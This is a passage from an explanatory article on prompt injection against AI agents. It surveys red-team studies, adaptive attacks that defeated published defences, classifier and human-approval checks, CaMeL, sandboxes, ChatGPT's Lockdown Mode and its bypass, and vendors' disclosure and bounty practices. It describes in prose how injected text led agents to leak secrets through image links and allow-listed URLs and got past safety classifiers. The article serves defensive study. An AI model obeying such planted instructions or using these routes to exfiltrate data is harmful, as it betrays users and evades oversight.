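Developers also use automated tools to find injections, and may advertise that an agent has faced thousands of successful attacks. A November 2026 study by a team from universities in Canada, China and Sweden suggests that many of these may be the same attack in different words (reported in Zorz, 2026, *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*).

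The researchers ran two published attack tools, PISmith and RL-Hammer, against the small model Qwen3-4B on 560 practice tasks. PISmith succeeded on 68.75% of the tasks and yielded 7,132 working attacks. RL-Hammer succeeded on 33.39% and yielded 4,282. The researchers then retrained one copy of the model on each collection of attacks and tested both copies with three attacks that neither copy had been trained on.

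The copy trained on the larger collection did worse. The most effective of the three attacks hijacked it in 19 of 40 tasks, compared with 11 of 40 for the other copy. Chance could explain a difference this small, and the researchers had chosen tasks in which simple attacks already worked on the original model. But the larger collection also produced the weaker agent in three of the four setups they tried, which makes chance a less likely explanation.

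The researchers think that once a tool finds a trick that works, it gets stuck applying it to one task after another. Both tools have checks to encourage variety, but these measure differences in wording. RL-Hammer's developers had noticed that it could satisfy the check by changing capital letters or adding irrelevant text. By the researchers' own measure, later attacks added little variety to either collection, and this began early on.

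The repeated scenarios had the same problem, but it is harder to see here. Dividing 720 attempts by ten is easy, whereas 7,132 differently worded attacks look like separate tests until somebody sorts them by technique. If they came from only a few dozen ideas, a bound calculated from the full number would be far too low.

The researchers built a system called PIPETTE that does this sorting and rewards the attack tool for finding a new technique. Fewer than 0.5% of ready-made attacks succeeded against agents trained with it on a standard set of everyday tasks. The researchers then tested attackers who kept trying, rewriting their injections about 250 times for each of the 40 difficult tasks. These attackers succeeded on up to 10% of the tasks. The first figure is a share of attempts and the second is a share of tasks, so the two aren't directly comparable.

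## Which defences have held when researchers attacked them?

In PIPETTE's own evaluation, its agents faced attackers who kept rewriting their injections until something worked. Most people who publish a defence instead run a fixed list of known attacks, or a general attack program that takes no account of how the defence works, as Nasr, Carlini and colleagues complained in *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025). A defence can pass such a test and still fail once an attacker studies it.

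How a defence fails depends on what it relies on. Some defences rely on a language model to resist or detect an attack, and others rely on a person to notice it. A few use ordinary program code to limit what a manipulated model can do, so they don't require the model or a person to detect the attack.

### Twelve defences against adaptive attackers

Nasr and colleagues, most of whom worked for OpenAI, Anthropic or Google DeepMind, attacked twelve published defences that depend on a model's judgement. RPO and Circuit Breakers are meant to stop jailbreaks, and the other ten deal with prompt injection.

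In each attack, the attacker tries some hostile texts, scores the results, and uses the best texts to write the next batch. In one version, a language model writes the texts and is trained with rewards for those that succeed. In another, a model makes small changes to the most successful texts over many generations. The researchers also tried calculating improvements from the target model's internal gradients, but found this less reliable. More than 500 people also attacked some of the defences by hand in an online competition.

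| Defence | Method | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Uses special markers to separate trusted from untrusted text | Over 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Over 95% |
| RPO | Adds an optimised warning to the prompt | 98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model against jailbreaks | 100% |
| StruQ | Trains the model to ignore instructions in data | 100% |
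| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model to resist injections as an agent | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Use a separate classifier to detect attacks | Over 90% each |
| PIGuard | Uses a separate classifier to detect attacks | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether a text distracts a model from repeating a secret key | Bypassed in every case |
| MELON | Runs the task twice and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

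In their original evaluations, most of these defences had attack success rates near zero. When Nasr and colleagues used the standard attacks from AgentDojo, a test in which agents work with simulated tools such as email and chat, the rates for Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching were as low as 1%. MetaSecAlign's developers had reported 2% on the same test.

One successful text presented the hostile action as a step the agent had to complete before it could do what the user wanted. Repeating the user's request didn't help because a model that treats the action as a required step will carry it out even if it is working only on the user's task. The classifiers missed similar texts because they read like ordinary office notes, and a classifier strict enough to catch them would also block a lot of harmless mail. Against MELON, the attack program produced a text that told the model to ignore the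 hostile instruction during MELON's check.

The attackers had advantages that most criminals would lack. They could use as much computing power as they liked, and they could tell from the classifiers' confidence scores when they were getting closer. Nasr and colleagues tested whether a defence could be broken, not how much effort that would take. They still recommend classifiers as one layer of protection, because these can stop unsophisticated attacks. The tests differed, so the percentages can't be used to rank the defences.

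On a selected set of scenarios and defences, the human participants collectively succeeded in every case, while the automated breeding method succeeded in 69%.

### Better-trained models

Model makers have since reported very different figures. Boris Cherny of Anthropic, whom Willison quotes, wrote in July 2026 that Opus 5 was "very hard to prompt inject successfully", and in the Trajectory Labs test no attack succeeded against Anthropic's newest models in auto mode. Outside evidence, such as Gray Swan's competition, also suggests that newer models are harder to attack.

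Both sets of results can be correct. Nasr and colleagues mostly tested defences that other researchers had added to existing models, whereas the leading companies train their own models against injections and keep updating the attacks they use. Research on image classifiers suggests that the updating matters. Training classifiers on a fixed collection of attacks failed, but training them against a program that kept searching for new attacks produced real resistance, at least to the kinds of attack it searched for.

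The makers' tests can still go out of date quickly, as Anthropic's browser test of November 2025 did. After Anthropic strengthened auto mode's classifier against Apollo Research's attacks, Apollo tested it again on a set of attacks that Anthropic had never seen. The classifier caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed, but missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. The improvement therefore extended to attacks Apollo hadn't shared, but this result doesn't show how the classifier would do against someone who studied the new version and designed attacks for it.

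Several of auto mode's other protections also depend on a model. A probe scans web pages and files for injections, but when it finds one, it only adds a warning to Claude's context window. Anthropic classes some actions, such as sending secrets outside, as "hard denies" that the classifier should never approve, but the classifier still has to recognise them.

Rehberger's attack of August 2026 got past the classifier with a series of steps that each looked harmless and together made Claude run hidden code. In a few runs, Claude noticed the malicious program and tried to stop it, but the classifier blocked its command. Anthropic didn't treat this as a security flaw. According to *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, the company replied that auto mode is a convenience feature with a best-effort classifier, which can't be expected to catch every such combination.

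### Asking a person

In August 2026, Anthropic published a study of how well people judge an agent's requests for approval, to support its decision to make auto mode the default.

A research company recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. Once per session, the software replaced the text of an ordinary approval request with a clearly dangerous command, though nothing dangerous ran if the tester approved it. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused. About 17% refused when the request came early in the session, compared with about 5% after 50 or more earlier requests.

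Auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%, including 800 that a person had approved. People refused only six of the 116 commands the classifier missed, or about 5%, which suggests that those commands were also harder for a person to recognise. Requiring approval from both would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6%, so adding a human check to the classifier would have made almost no difference.

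Programmers may be more careful on their own computers than the testers, who were not working on their own projects and had nothing to lose. The comparison also leaves out how often the classifier blocked harmless commands, so a classifier that blocked everything would have scored 100%.

Data from real use suggests that inattention is common outside the study too. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission requests, although most of these are probably harmless. A quarter of interactive sessions start with the requests turned off. Anthropic also examined sessions that its safety systems had flagged. It found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This is weaker evidence than the controlled study, because users chose the mode themselves and a model graded the harm.

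Willison accepted that people can't be expected to approve an action every few steps, but pointed out that the classifier had still missed 11% of the dangerous commands.

People may review an agent's requests better when it asks them to approve fewer, larger decisions. When Claude presents a whole plan for approval, users reject it 39% of the time. Some probably reject it for reasons unrelated to security, but they do seem to have read it.

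### How CaMeL separates plans from data

Researchers at Google DeepMind and their collaborators published CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning", in March 2025. CaMeL assumes that an injection may deceive a model and uses ordinary code to limit the consequences. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, wrote that before CaMeL he had seen "alarmingly little progress" on robust solutions.

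CaMeL builds on Willison's 2023 proposal to divide the work between two models. A privileged model plans the task without ever seeing untrusted text, and a quarantined model, which has no tools, reads that text. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who wants to find Bob's email address in a chat channel and tell him about a meeting at 3pm.

The privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted version of Python. In simplified form, it looks like this:

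```
messages = read_channel("general")
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find Bob's email address", messages)
send_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

An interpreter, an ordinary program that carries out such code line by line, then runs the plan. It fetches the messages and stores them as `messages`, without showing them to the privileged model. It then gives them to the quarantined model, which must return an email address. The interpreter stores this as `address` and sends the message.

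Suppose an attacker has posted a message in the channel with an instruction to find the company's salary file and email it to an outside address. The quarantined model may well try to follow the instruction, but it can't open files or send anything. The privileged model never receives the instruction, and the plan has no step for opening the salary file. At worst, the attacker can make the quarantined model return a wrong address for Bob.

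That would still send the message to the attacker, so CaMeL also labels every piece of data with its source and who may read it. The address's label shows that it came from the chat channel. Before the interpreter sends the message, it runs a policy, a short function that checks the tool, the data and the labels to allow or refuse the action. A policy could require that a recipient's address come from the user or the company directory. The interpreter would then refuse to use an address from the channel or, as the technology news site TechSpot explains, could ask the user to confirm it.

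This protection has drawbacks even without an attack. The revised version of *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, the paper that introduced CaMeL, reports that the system completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an agent without the defence. The fixed plan is a particular problem when a user asks an agent to do whatever an email requests, because the steps depend on text that the planning model isn't allowed to read. Somebody also has to write the policies. If the policies are too strict, the user gets many confirmation requests and may stop reading them, as the testers in Anthropic's study did.

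CaMeL checks each action only when the agent is about to perform it, so Nikolaou and colleagues added a tool that examines the whole plan before it runs. If a plan would disconnect a computer from the network without first getting approval, the tool can reject it before the agent spends an hour on the earlier steps. It can also enforce rules about the whole task, such as requiring the agent to close every incident ticket it opens. The tool simplifies loops to keep the analysis manageable, so it may reject some safe plans.

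Nasr and colleagues didn't include CaMeL among the twelve defences they tested, although five of these researchers had helped to develop it. The case for its security therefore rests mainly on its design, which is easier to reason about than a model's training, rather than on its having survived determined attacks. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that features of Python make it hard to guarantee where data can flow. CaMeL also doesn't stop a hostile document from causing a false summary, because the quarantined model still has to read the document and may be misled by it.

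*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) describes a paper by 11 researchers from organisations including IBM, Google, Microsoft and ETH Zurich. The paper's designs also trade capability for security. They deliberately prevent an agent from solving arbitrary tasks to make it more secure on the tasks it can still do.

### Meta's Rule of Two

CaMeL requires a new way of building agents. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) instead gives developers a rule for deciding what an agent may do. Until models can reliably detect and refuse injections, an agent that works without supervision should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

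- It processes untrusted input.
- It has access to private data or sensitive systems.
- It can change things or communicate with the outside.

Meta applies this to an email assistant that an attacker could otherwise trick into forwarding the user's mail. The developer could let the assistant read messages only from trusted senders, or run it in a test environment with no private data. Or they could let it send mail only to trusted recipients, or only after a person has checked the draft.

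The Rule of Two is based partly on Willison's lethal trifecta, but it also covers agents that change things without sending data out. One example is the Word worm, in which Copilot read an outside document, had access to the company's figures and altered them in a report. Under the rule, Copilot would have needed supervision. The user did have a chance to read the report before sharing it, but might easily have missed the changes.

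Meta warns that people may confirm warnings without reading them, and Anthropic's study suggests that they usually do. So the rule offers much less protection when an agent has all three properties and relies on a person to confirm its actions.

Developers also have to know what their agent can reach. An attacker could get from Cline's AI triage job to the publishing credentials through a shared cache. A developer might have missed this and concluded that the job had only two of the properties, because it seemed to hold nothing more valuable than a key for using Claude.

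Memory creates a similar problem. Meta's rule applies to a session and treats a fresh context window as a clean start, but instructions planted in an agent's memory carry over into the next session. Developers would have to treat that memory as untrusted too.

### Sandboxes

Replying to Rehberger about auto mode, Anthropic said that the real security boundary is operating system isolation and control of network traffic. A sandbox provides both. If an injected agent tries to read a file outside its permitted folder, the operating system blocks the attempt, however convincing the injection was.

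Rehberger recommends running unattended coding agents in a sandbox or virtual machine, restricting which servers they can contact, and denying them access to login keys and personal folders. Willison agrees that this is the only safe way to run an agent that attackers might target.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that sandboxes take work to set up and maintain because someone has to configure each new capability, and that access to the network or the host computer weakens the isolation. An agent often needs both. A programmer may want it to download software packages, and an office assistant is of little use if it can't send email. *Operationalizing CaMeL* notes that if a sandbox permits email, an injected agent can still put sensitive data in a plausible message. CaMeL's labels can control what goes into that message, while a sandbox controls only whether the agent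 may use email.

Researchers have also found flaws in the isolation itself. In March 2026, Check Point, a security company that sells protection for AI systems, described a hidden connection to the public internet from the sandbox, or isolated environment, where ChatGPT runs code. *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (Check Point Research, 2026) reports that a single malicious prompt could use this connection to leak the user's messages and uploaded files. In September, Check Point Research reported another hidden channel, between different users' accounts. Cato AI Labs also broke out of Copilot's sandbox in summer 2026.

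### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for business and institutional customers in February 2026 and began extending it to personal accounts in June. The optional setting is meant for people at higher risk of attack, such as executives and security teams. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) states that the mode "deterministically disables" features an attacker could use to steal data, meaning that fixed rules turn them off rather than a model deciding case by case.

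In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT can read only stored copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. This should stop both the long address that carries stolen data and the letter-by-letter trick, because both rely on visits to the attacker's server. ChatGPT also can't display images in ordinary answers, which blocks the oldest way of stealing data. It can't download files for analysis, and code it writes in its Canvas editor can't connect to the network. Agent Mode and Deep Research, which carry out longer tasks on the web, are off. For personal accounts, Lockdown Mode also blocks live access to connected services and any actions in other apps that conflict with its protections.

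OpenAI doesn't claim that any of this stops prompt injection. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, a hostile instruction in an uploaded file or a stored web page can still make ChatGPT give a wrong answer. The mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory or restrict network access in Codex. It also doesn't automatically turn off connected apps in company-managed workspaces, so an administrator has to decide which ones to allow. OpenAI warns that data could still leak through these apps, unforeseen combinations of features or new methods.

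Willison (2026) welcomed the mode because a clever prompt can't override fixed rules. He also concluded that ChatGPT's ordinary settings don't provide robust protection against a determined data thief.

On 5 November 2026, Check Point disclosed a way around ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) explains that the flaw was in a feature that can display a web page inside the chat when ChatGPT's answer contains the page's code. Because such code could be hostile, ChatGPT ran it in a sandboxed frame, a section of the window that couldn't read the application's data or contact outside servers without the user's consent.

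ChatGPT intercepted direct attempts to open a new window from the frame, but the sandbox's permissions still allowed new windows and exempted them from its restrictions. Check Point's researchers wrote a page that created a second frame inside the first. The inner frame had a fresh copy of the function for opening windows, which ChatGPT didn't intercept. A window opened with that copy could connect to the attacker's server and send data from the chat.

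An attacker could deliver the page through a crafted prompt, a shared chat or a malicious GPT (a customised version of ChatGPT made by someone else). In the desktop application, the theft worked without the user clicking anything. The attacker could also use the new window to show a fake ChatGPT update and persuade the user to install malware. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September, seven weeks before Check Point published it. The fix was made on OpenAI's own servers, according to TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment*.

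The preview gave the attacker another way to reach the internet, so the attack worked without breaking the browsing restrictions or persuading a model to lift them. ChatGPT intercepted one function to block this route but left the underlying permission in place. If the sandbox had forbidden new windows altogether, the second copy of the function would have been useless.

A week earlier, the firm Parameter Labs had disclosed another flaw in the preview feature. A link to a shared chat could run an attacker's code with the victim's ChatGPT login if the victim opened the link and, in some cases, clicked on the preview. Check Point told The Hacker News that the two flaws were different but affected the same component.

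### What survives a mistake in the code

A sandbox can't guarantee that data stays inside it if the code enforcing that guarantee has an error. But such an error is in a specific part of the code, so OpenAI could find the faulty preview code and repair it for everyone at once. When an injection succeeds against a model, the model's maker can train it further, but can't identify the exact mistake or prove that a differently worded injection will fail.

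Limits that remove something from an agent's reach are less fragile than barriers around the agent. If an agent has no private data, a hole in its sandbox exposes none. ChatGPT Atlas's logged-out mode protects the user's accounts in this way. Companies can still make mistakes when they remove access, as Cline did when it deleted the wrong token, but such a mistake is fairly easy to detect because someone can try the token that should have been deleted and see whether it still works.

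CaMeL could withstand some errors but not others. If a developer writes a policy that is too permissive, an attacker may be able to redirect the message meant for Bob. The attacker still can't add a step that opens the salary file, because the privileged model wrote the plan before the system processed the hostile text. An error in the interpreter could be much worse, since the interpreter enforces both the plan and the labels.

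Combining several limits helps only if one error can't defeat them all. In Snowflake's Cortex, command approval and the sandbox relied on the same checker, so one error could defeat both. A coding agent is better protected on a machine that holds no passwords, behind a firewall that the agent can't change. An attacker could then steal a password only if somebody had left one on the machine by mistake and the firewall also had a hole.

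## What happens when a researcher reports a flaw?

Check Point waited until OpenAI had fixed the flaw in ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode before publishing its findings. In this practice, called coordinated disclosure, the finder tells the maker first and publishes after a fix or an agreed period. The practice developed around ordinary software, and it worked here because the flaw was an ordinary software error. Reports about prompt injection often go less smoothly.

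### Disclosure in ordinary software

Suppose a researcher finds that a photo program runs hidden code when it opens a certain damaged file. She privately sends the maker the file, the program's version number and the steps to reproduce the flaw. An engineer opens the file in the same version and sees the code run, so nobody has to argue about whether the flaw exists.

The maker then rates how serious the flaw is, usually with the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). An assessor answers a fixed set of questions about whether an attacker can reach the program over a network, whether the attack is complex, whether it needs an account or an action by the victim, and how badly it affects the secrecy, accuracy and availability of data. A formula turns the answers into a score from 0 to 10. In version 3.1, a simple attack over the internet that exposes confidential data but changes nothing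 scores 7.5 if the victim does nothing and 6.5 if the victim has to act. SearchLeak received two different scores because of different answers about whether the victim had to act.

The developer releases a fixed version, and the flaw receives a CVE, its identifier in the public catalogue. The catalogue entry lists the affected versions, so a company can check whether any of its computers still run one.

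The researcher publishes the flaw once the maker has fixed it, or after about 90 days if it hasn't. Without a deadline, a maker could leave the flaw unfixed indefinitely while its users didn't know they needed to protect themselves. Researchers often extend the deadline if the repair is progressing, as Måløy did twice for the Word worm.

### Where prompt injection doesn't fit

An injection that worked for the researcher may fail when the maker's engineer tries it, because a model's output varies. OpenAI (2026) therefore accepts reports of injections that hijack a victim's agent only if the behaviour is "reproducible at least 50% of the time".

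The announcement doesn't specify a number of attempts, and luck matters a lot in a short test. If the engineer tries ten times, an attack that works 60% of the time has about a one-in-six chance of succeeding fewer than five times. An attack that works 40% of the time, roughly the rate reported for Adversa's attack on Grok, has more than a one-in-three chance of succeeding at least five times. The threshold also excludes attacks that would still be useful to an attacker. A hostile email that works one time in ten would hijack about 100 assistants if it were sent to 1,000 people whose assistants all read it.

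The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) doesn't record an attack's success rate. The closest metric is attack complexity, which an assessor must rate as either low or high. For example, a data theft flaw that scores 7.5 with low complexity would score 5.9 with high complexity. Two assessors could reasonably disagree about which rating to give an injection that works half the time.

Fixing the flaw is a bigger problem, because a company can't correct a model the way it would correct the photo program's code. So someone at the company has to decide whether a report describes a flaw or just a known property of language models.

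Google's *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules* made a similar distinction for its products in general between security vulnerabilities, which are loopholes that require a fix, and abuse risks, which are "often inherent to product features". Google would often leave such a feature on and try to stop people from exploiting it at scale. OpenAI reasoned similarly in 2023 and 2024, when it told Rehberger that displaying images was a feature and that false memories were a model safety issue.

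Most assistants also run on the maker's servers, where the maker can change them at any time without telling anyone. A researcher whose attack stops working may not know whether the maker has repaired the flaw, replaced the model or added a filter that recognises one wording. There may be no version number to put in a CVE entry, and customers have nothing to install. Flaws in hosted services can still receive CVEs, as EchoLeak did in Microsoft's Copilot. For customers, such an entry is mainly a public record that their data was at risk.

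Finally, the same injection may work on products from many companies. Guan's team used an attack called Comment and Control on tools from Anthropic, Google and GitHub. The Hacker News' *Google Patches Antigravity IDE Flaw* (2026) quotes a warning that the attack probably works on any agent that reads untrusted text on GitHub and can run tools where a project keeps its secrets. Researchers can't privately warn every company that has built such an agent, and the more companies they warn, the greater the risk that the flaw leaks before the products are fixed.

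Sometimes the affected companies can't fix the cause of a flaw themselves. For example, Gemini models obey invisible text, a weakness that also affected Jules. According to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*, Google had not addressed this in the model or in the interface that developers use, so every application built on Gemini inherited it.

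### The report on OpenAI's API logs

Developers who build applications on OpenAI's models can read past conversations in a log viewer on OpenAI's website. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes how this viewer displayed Markdown images from any address, the same weakness Samoilenko found in ChatGPT in 2023.

PromptArmor built a mock application of the kind banks use to verify customers' identities. Its assistant read a customer's personal and financial details along with material from the internet that contained a prompt injection. The injection made the assistant write an image link with the customer's details in the URL. As a safeguard, a second language model checked each answer. It blocked this one, so the user's browser never loaded the image, and flagged the conversation for review.

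When a developer opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's viewer, the developer's browser loaded the image and sent the customer's details to the attacker's server. Other safeguards could fail in the same way. If an application removed the image, the user might click "thumbs down" on the oddly empty answer, and a developer might then open the log. PromptArmor found the same display flaw in the previews that developers use to test new agents and in a starter application that OpenAI provided.

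PromptArmor reported its findings on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that receives and sorts reports for OpenAI. It supplied step-by-step instructions three days later and answered questions on three more days. On 4 December, the report was closed as "Not applicable", and PromptArmor published its findings so that developers could take precautions.

OpenAI had never seen the report, because Bugcrowd had handled it. After seeing the article, OpenAI confirmed the flaw. It reopened the report on 22 January 2026, 66 days after the first submission, and said a fix was under way.

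PromptArmor was fairly understanding about the mistake and wrote that prompt injections are often hard to classify under existing categories. But this report should have been easier to classify than most. The viewer loaded images from strangers' servers, and OpenAI could stop that with ordinary code, as Microsoft had done for Bing Chat in 2023. The injection may have obscured this because it entered through someone else's web page and misled an assistant in someone else's application. A person sorting reports could easily conclude that OpenAI wasn't responsible.

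PromptArmor doesn't report how often the assistant wrote the link, and it demonstrated the full attack only on its own application. These limitations matter little for the repair, because the viewer would load the image whenever it received such a link.

### Google's list of known issues

In November 2025, Google released Antigravity, a code editor with built-in agents. It was based on Windsurf, an editor whose code Google had licensed. Rehberger had reported several flaws to Windsurf that May, before Google licensed the code, and he found that they were still present in Antigravity. He published five weaknesses a week after the release. Antigravity let the model decide which commands were safe to run, followed instructions written in invisible text, used connected tools without asking the user, and could leak data both by opening web addresses and by displaying images.

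Rehberger had some trouble proving that the commands were dangerous. The usual demonstration, starting the calculator, is harmless, so a model that does it hasn't necessarily made an error. When he tried to download and run a script from the internet, the models often refused. He eventually found a method that worked on Gemini 3 and Claude Sonnet 4.5.

By then Google had published a page of known issues, which was quoted in a Hacker News thread. On it, Google acknowledged that untrusted text could lead the agent to run malicious commands or leak files. Google described the agent as cautious with sensitive files but added that "there's no enforcement". It also wrote that it was working on fixes and would not reward reports of these issues. Willison noted that another researcher, who goes by P1njc70r, had reported the image leak and said that Google had marked it as intended behaviour.

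Google (2023) had already excluded known problems when it set out which AI flaws it would pay for. The rule makes sense for a bounty scheme, which pays people to tell a company something it doesn't know. Without it, dozens of people would have reported the image leak. Google also warned users about data theft when they first opened Antigravity.

PromptArmor thought the warning was no substitute for protection. In its *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, a user asked Antigravity's agent to follow an online guide for connecting their program to an Oracle product. The guide contained an injection in one-point type. Antigravity's default settings prevented the agent from opening the file where the user kept passwords and keys, so the agent displayed the file with a terminal command instead. It then put the contents into a web address and opened that address in Antigravity's browser. Google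 had included webhook.site on the browser's allow-list, and anyone can create an address there and read the requests sent to it.

The attack worked on the settings Google recommended to new users, which let the agent decide when to ask a person for approval. The warning seemed to rely on users checking every action, which PromptArmor found extremely implausible because one of Antigravity's main features is a screen for managing several agents that work in the background.

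PromptArmor did not report the attack privately because Google had indicated that it knew of such risks. A broad list of known risks predictably has this effect, since anyone who finds a new route it covers gets no reward for reporting it and may see no reason to wait before publishing. But some of those routes are specific mistakes that Google could correct in minutes. For example, it could remove webhook.site from the allow-list without making the model better at resisting injections.

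Google did pay for a different flaw in the same product. Pillar Security, which sells security for AI systems, found that an injection could run code even in Secure Mode, a stricter setting, because the attack's call never went through the mode's checks. Pillar reported this on 6 January 2026. Google released a patch on 28 February and paid a bounty, according to CyberScoop. The flaw was much harder to call a known property of the product because it was in a restriction that Google had told users they could rely on.

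The problems on the list lasted longer. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026), published nearly seven months after the list, describes another data theft that combined Antigravity's terminal, browser and image display. Odson and Morris hid the instructions in a web page's title and made them look like an error log with a recovery procedure.

### Other responses, and how long repairs took

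xAI was less forthcoming than Google. In 2024 Rehberger spent several weeks answering its questions about data leaks and manipulated answers in Grok. xAI closed all his reports as "Informational", and Willison concluded that it didn't seem to be taking the problem seriously. The same month, Anthropic fixed an image leak that Rehberger had reported in Claude's iPhone app.

Cursor, which makes a coding agent, called an attack by Zenity Labs "a known issue" in 2025. The attacker sent a company a support email containing hidden instructions, and the email automatically became a ticket in the system where the company's programmers track their work. When a programmer asked the agent to look at the ticket, the instructions could make it send out an access token. Cursor advised connecting the agent only to tools that read trusted content. Willison objected that this advice is hard to follow because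 attackers have so many ways to get text into a system. For example, a programmer would probably think of the ticket tracker as internal, even though it contains text from outsiders.

Salesforce fixed a data leak that Noma Security had found in its Agentforce assistant. The researchers had put instructions into a form that companies use to collect enquiries from potential customers. Salesforce's list of domains allowed for images still included one whose registration had lapsed, so the researchers registered it and received the stolen data there. Salesforce corrected the list and then stopped the agent from producing links to untrusted addresses.

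The table compares these dates for Pillar's report and seven cases from earlier sections.

| Flaw | Reported | Repaired | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Superhuman's image leak | 5 December 2025 | 9 December 2025 (first patch) | 4 days |
| Snowflake Cortex's command checker | 5 February 2026 | 28 February 2026 | 23 days |
| Cline's issue triage | 1 January 2026 | 9 February 2026 | 39 days |
| GitHub Copilot's settings file | 29 June 2025 | 12 August 2025 | 44 days |
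| Antigravity's Secure Mode | 6 January 2026 | 28 February 2026 | 53 days |
| Bing Chat's image leak | 8 April 2023 | By 15 June 2023 | At most 68 days |
| ChatGPT's image leak | 9 April 2023 | December 2023 (partly) | 8 months |
| Copilot's Word worm | 6 March 2026 | Not by 28 July 2026 | Over 144 days |

Researchers chose which of these cases to write up, so they don't show a typical repair time. But the makers that fixed their flaws within the usual 90 days all had something definite to change, such as a list of addresses or a faulty check. Microsoft had nothing so definite to change for the Word worm, and its two attempts to alter how Copilot responded to the hidden text both failed. Delays can also have nothing to do with the difficulty of the repair, as with Cline, which needed only 30 minutes once Khan had published.

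### What the companies pay for

OpenAI runs separate reward schemes for security flaws and for what it calls safety issues. In March 2025, it raised its highest security reward from $20,000 to $100,000 (OpenAI, *Security on the path to AGI*). In November 2026, it also raised most of the lower rewards. A critical flaw in ChatGPT, Codex or the API can now earn up to $30,000, and an exceptional one still up to $100,000 (Pogorelec, 2026, *OpenAI raises top bug bounty payout to $172,000 with bonuses*). OpenAI also pays bonuses for well-written reports and to researchers who keep contributing.

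The safety scheme, open since March 2026, accepts some problems that don't count as security vulnerabilities, including third-party injections that make an agent leak data or take a harmful action, subject to the 50% threshold. Reports can move between the two schemes, so a researcher may not know in advance which rules will apply. OpenAI excludes jailbreaks from the public safety scheme but pays for some of them privately. In July 2026 it doubled the reward for a universal jailbreak of its biology safeguards to $50,000 (OpenAI, 2026), which is more than it normally pays for a critical security flaw.

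In October 2025, Google introduced a reward program for AI flaws in which payments depend on the product's tier. SecurityWeek reports that, for flagship products, Google pays up to $20,000 for an attack that changes a victim's account or data and up to $15,000 for one that steals sensitive data. The same theft from a product in the lowest tier earns at most $10,000. A single panel now considers each report under both the abuse and security rules and awards the higher amount. Researchers therefore no longer receive less when Google classifies an injection as abuse, though known issues still earn nothing.

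Microsoft and Anthropic have varied from case to case in what they treat as a vulnerability. Microsoft treated EchoLeak as one, whereas its subsidiary GitHub called Guan's finding an architectural limitation but still paid for it. Anthropic's rewards to Guan and RyotaK didn't follow its severity ratings. It declined to treat Rehberger's way around auto mode as a security flaw because it doesn't present auto mode as a security boundary. The same reasoning worked in Pillar's favour at Google, so a maker's decision can depend more on what it has promised than on what an attacker can do.

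Reviewers now have many more reports to read. *GitHub restructures bug bounty program following flood of AI-generated reports* (Hale, 2026) describes how GitHub split its scheme into a public and a private one in July 2026. Google froze its bounty for open-source software that autumn, and *Google's Open-Source Bug Bounty Program Has A Big AI Problem* (Garland, 2026) reports complaints from technology companies that poorly researched, AI-written reports make real flaws harder to find. An injection report is easy to mistake for one of these, since the attack may fail on the first try and the evidence is often a screenshot of a chat. OpenAI's extra payment for a reliable demonstration should help, but it favours attacks that work nearly every time.

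### Proposals for reporting AI flaws

*In-House Evaluation Is Not Enough* (2025) proposes a flaw-reporting system designed for AI. Shayne Longpre, a doctoral student at MIT, wrote it with colleagues from Stanford and a dozen other institutions. In Stanford HAI's *A Framework to Report AI's Flaws*, Longpre argues that AI companies' methods for finding and fixing flaws lag far behind those in cybersecurity.

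The group wants researchers to report flaws on a standard form that records the system and its version, what went wrong, how to reproduce it and which of the maker's policies it violates. It also wants companies to accept reports on a much wider range of problems than security flaws, and to legally protect people who test in good faith. It proposes a shared centre that would pass each report to every company the flaw might affect.

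A standard form would have helped with the API logs if it had made clear that the fault was in OpenAI's viewer and not in the mock application. For injections, the form would also need to include the number of attempts and successes, because "reproducible" means little without them. The shared centre would help when one attack works on many products, but it would have to decide whom to tell. If it told 50 companies about an unrepaired injection, one of them might leak it, and the first company's repair could reveal the method before the others had finished theirs. Ordinary software has the same problem when many products share a faulty component, but it is probably worse here because some of the companies may never have a complete repair.

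HackerOne, which runs bug bounty schemes for other companies, took part in the workshop that led to the paper and endorsed its proposals, as Cohen and Sherrets explain in *HackerOne Joins Call for Action on AI Third-Party Evaluation and Flaw Disclosure*. HackerOne would gain business if more companies opened such schemes.

OpenAI's 2026 safety scheme covers part of the wider scope that Longpre and colleagues asked for, but it excludes most jailbreaks and any injection that works less than half the time. In October 2026 OpenAI also published a five-stage plan for handling flaws that AI finds in software. Under this plan, the software's maintainers decide who learns of a flaw first (Zorz, 2026, *AI-found bugs are expected to rise, and OpenAI has a five-stage response*). A shared centre would instead warn everyone affected. A year after the proposals, Anthropic, Google and GitHub still handled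 Comment and Control separately and issued no public advisory, which might have warned the makers of similar tools.

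## Who does this research, and what protects them?

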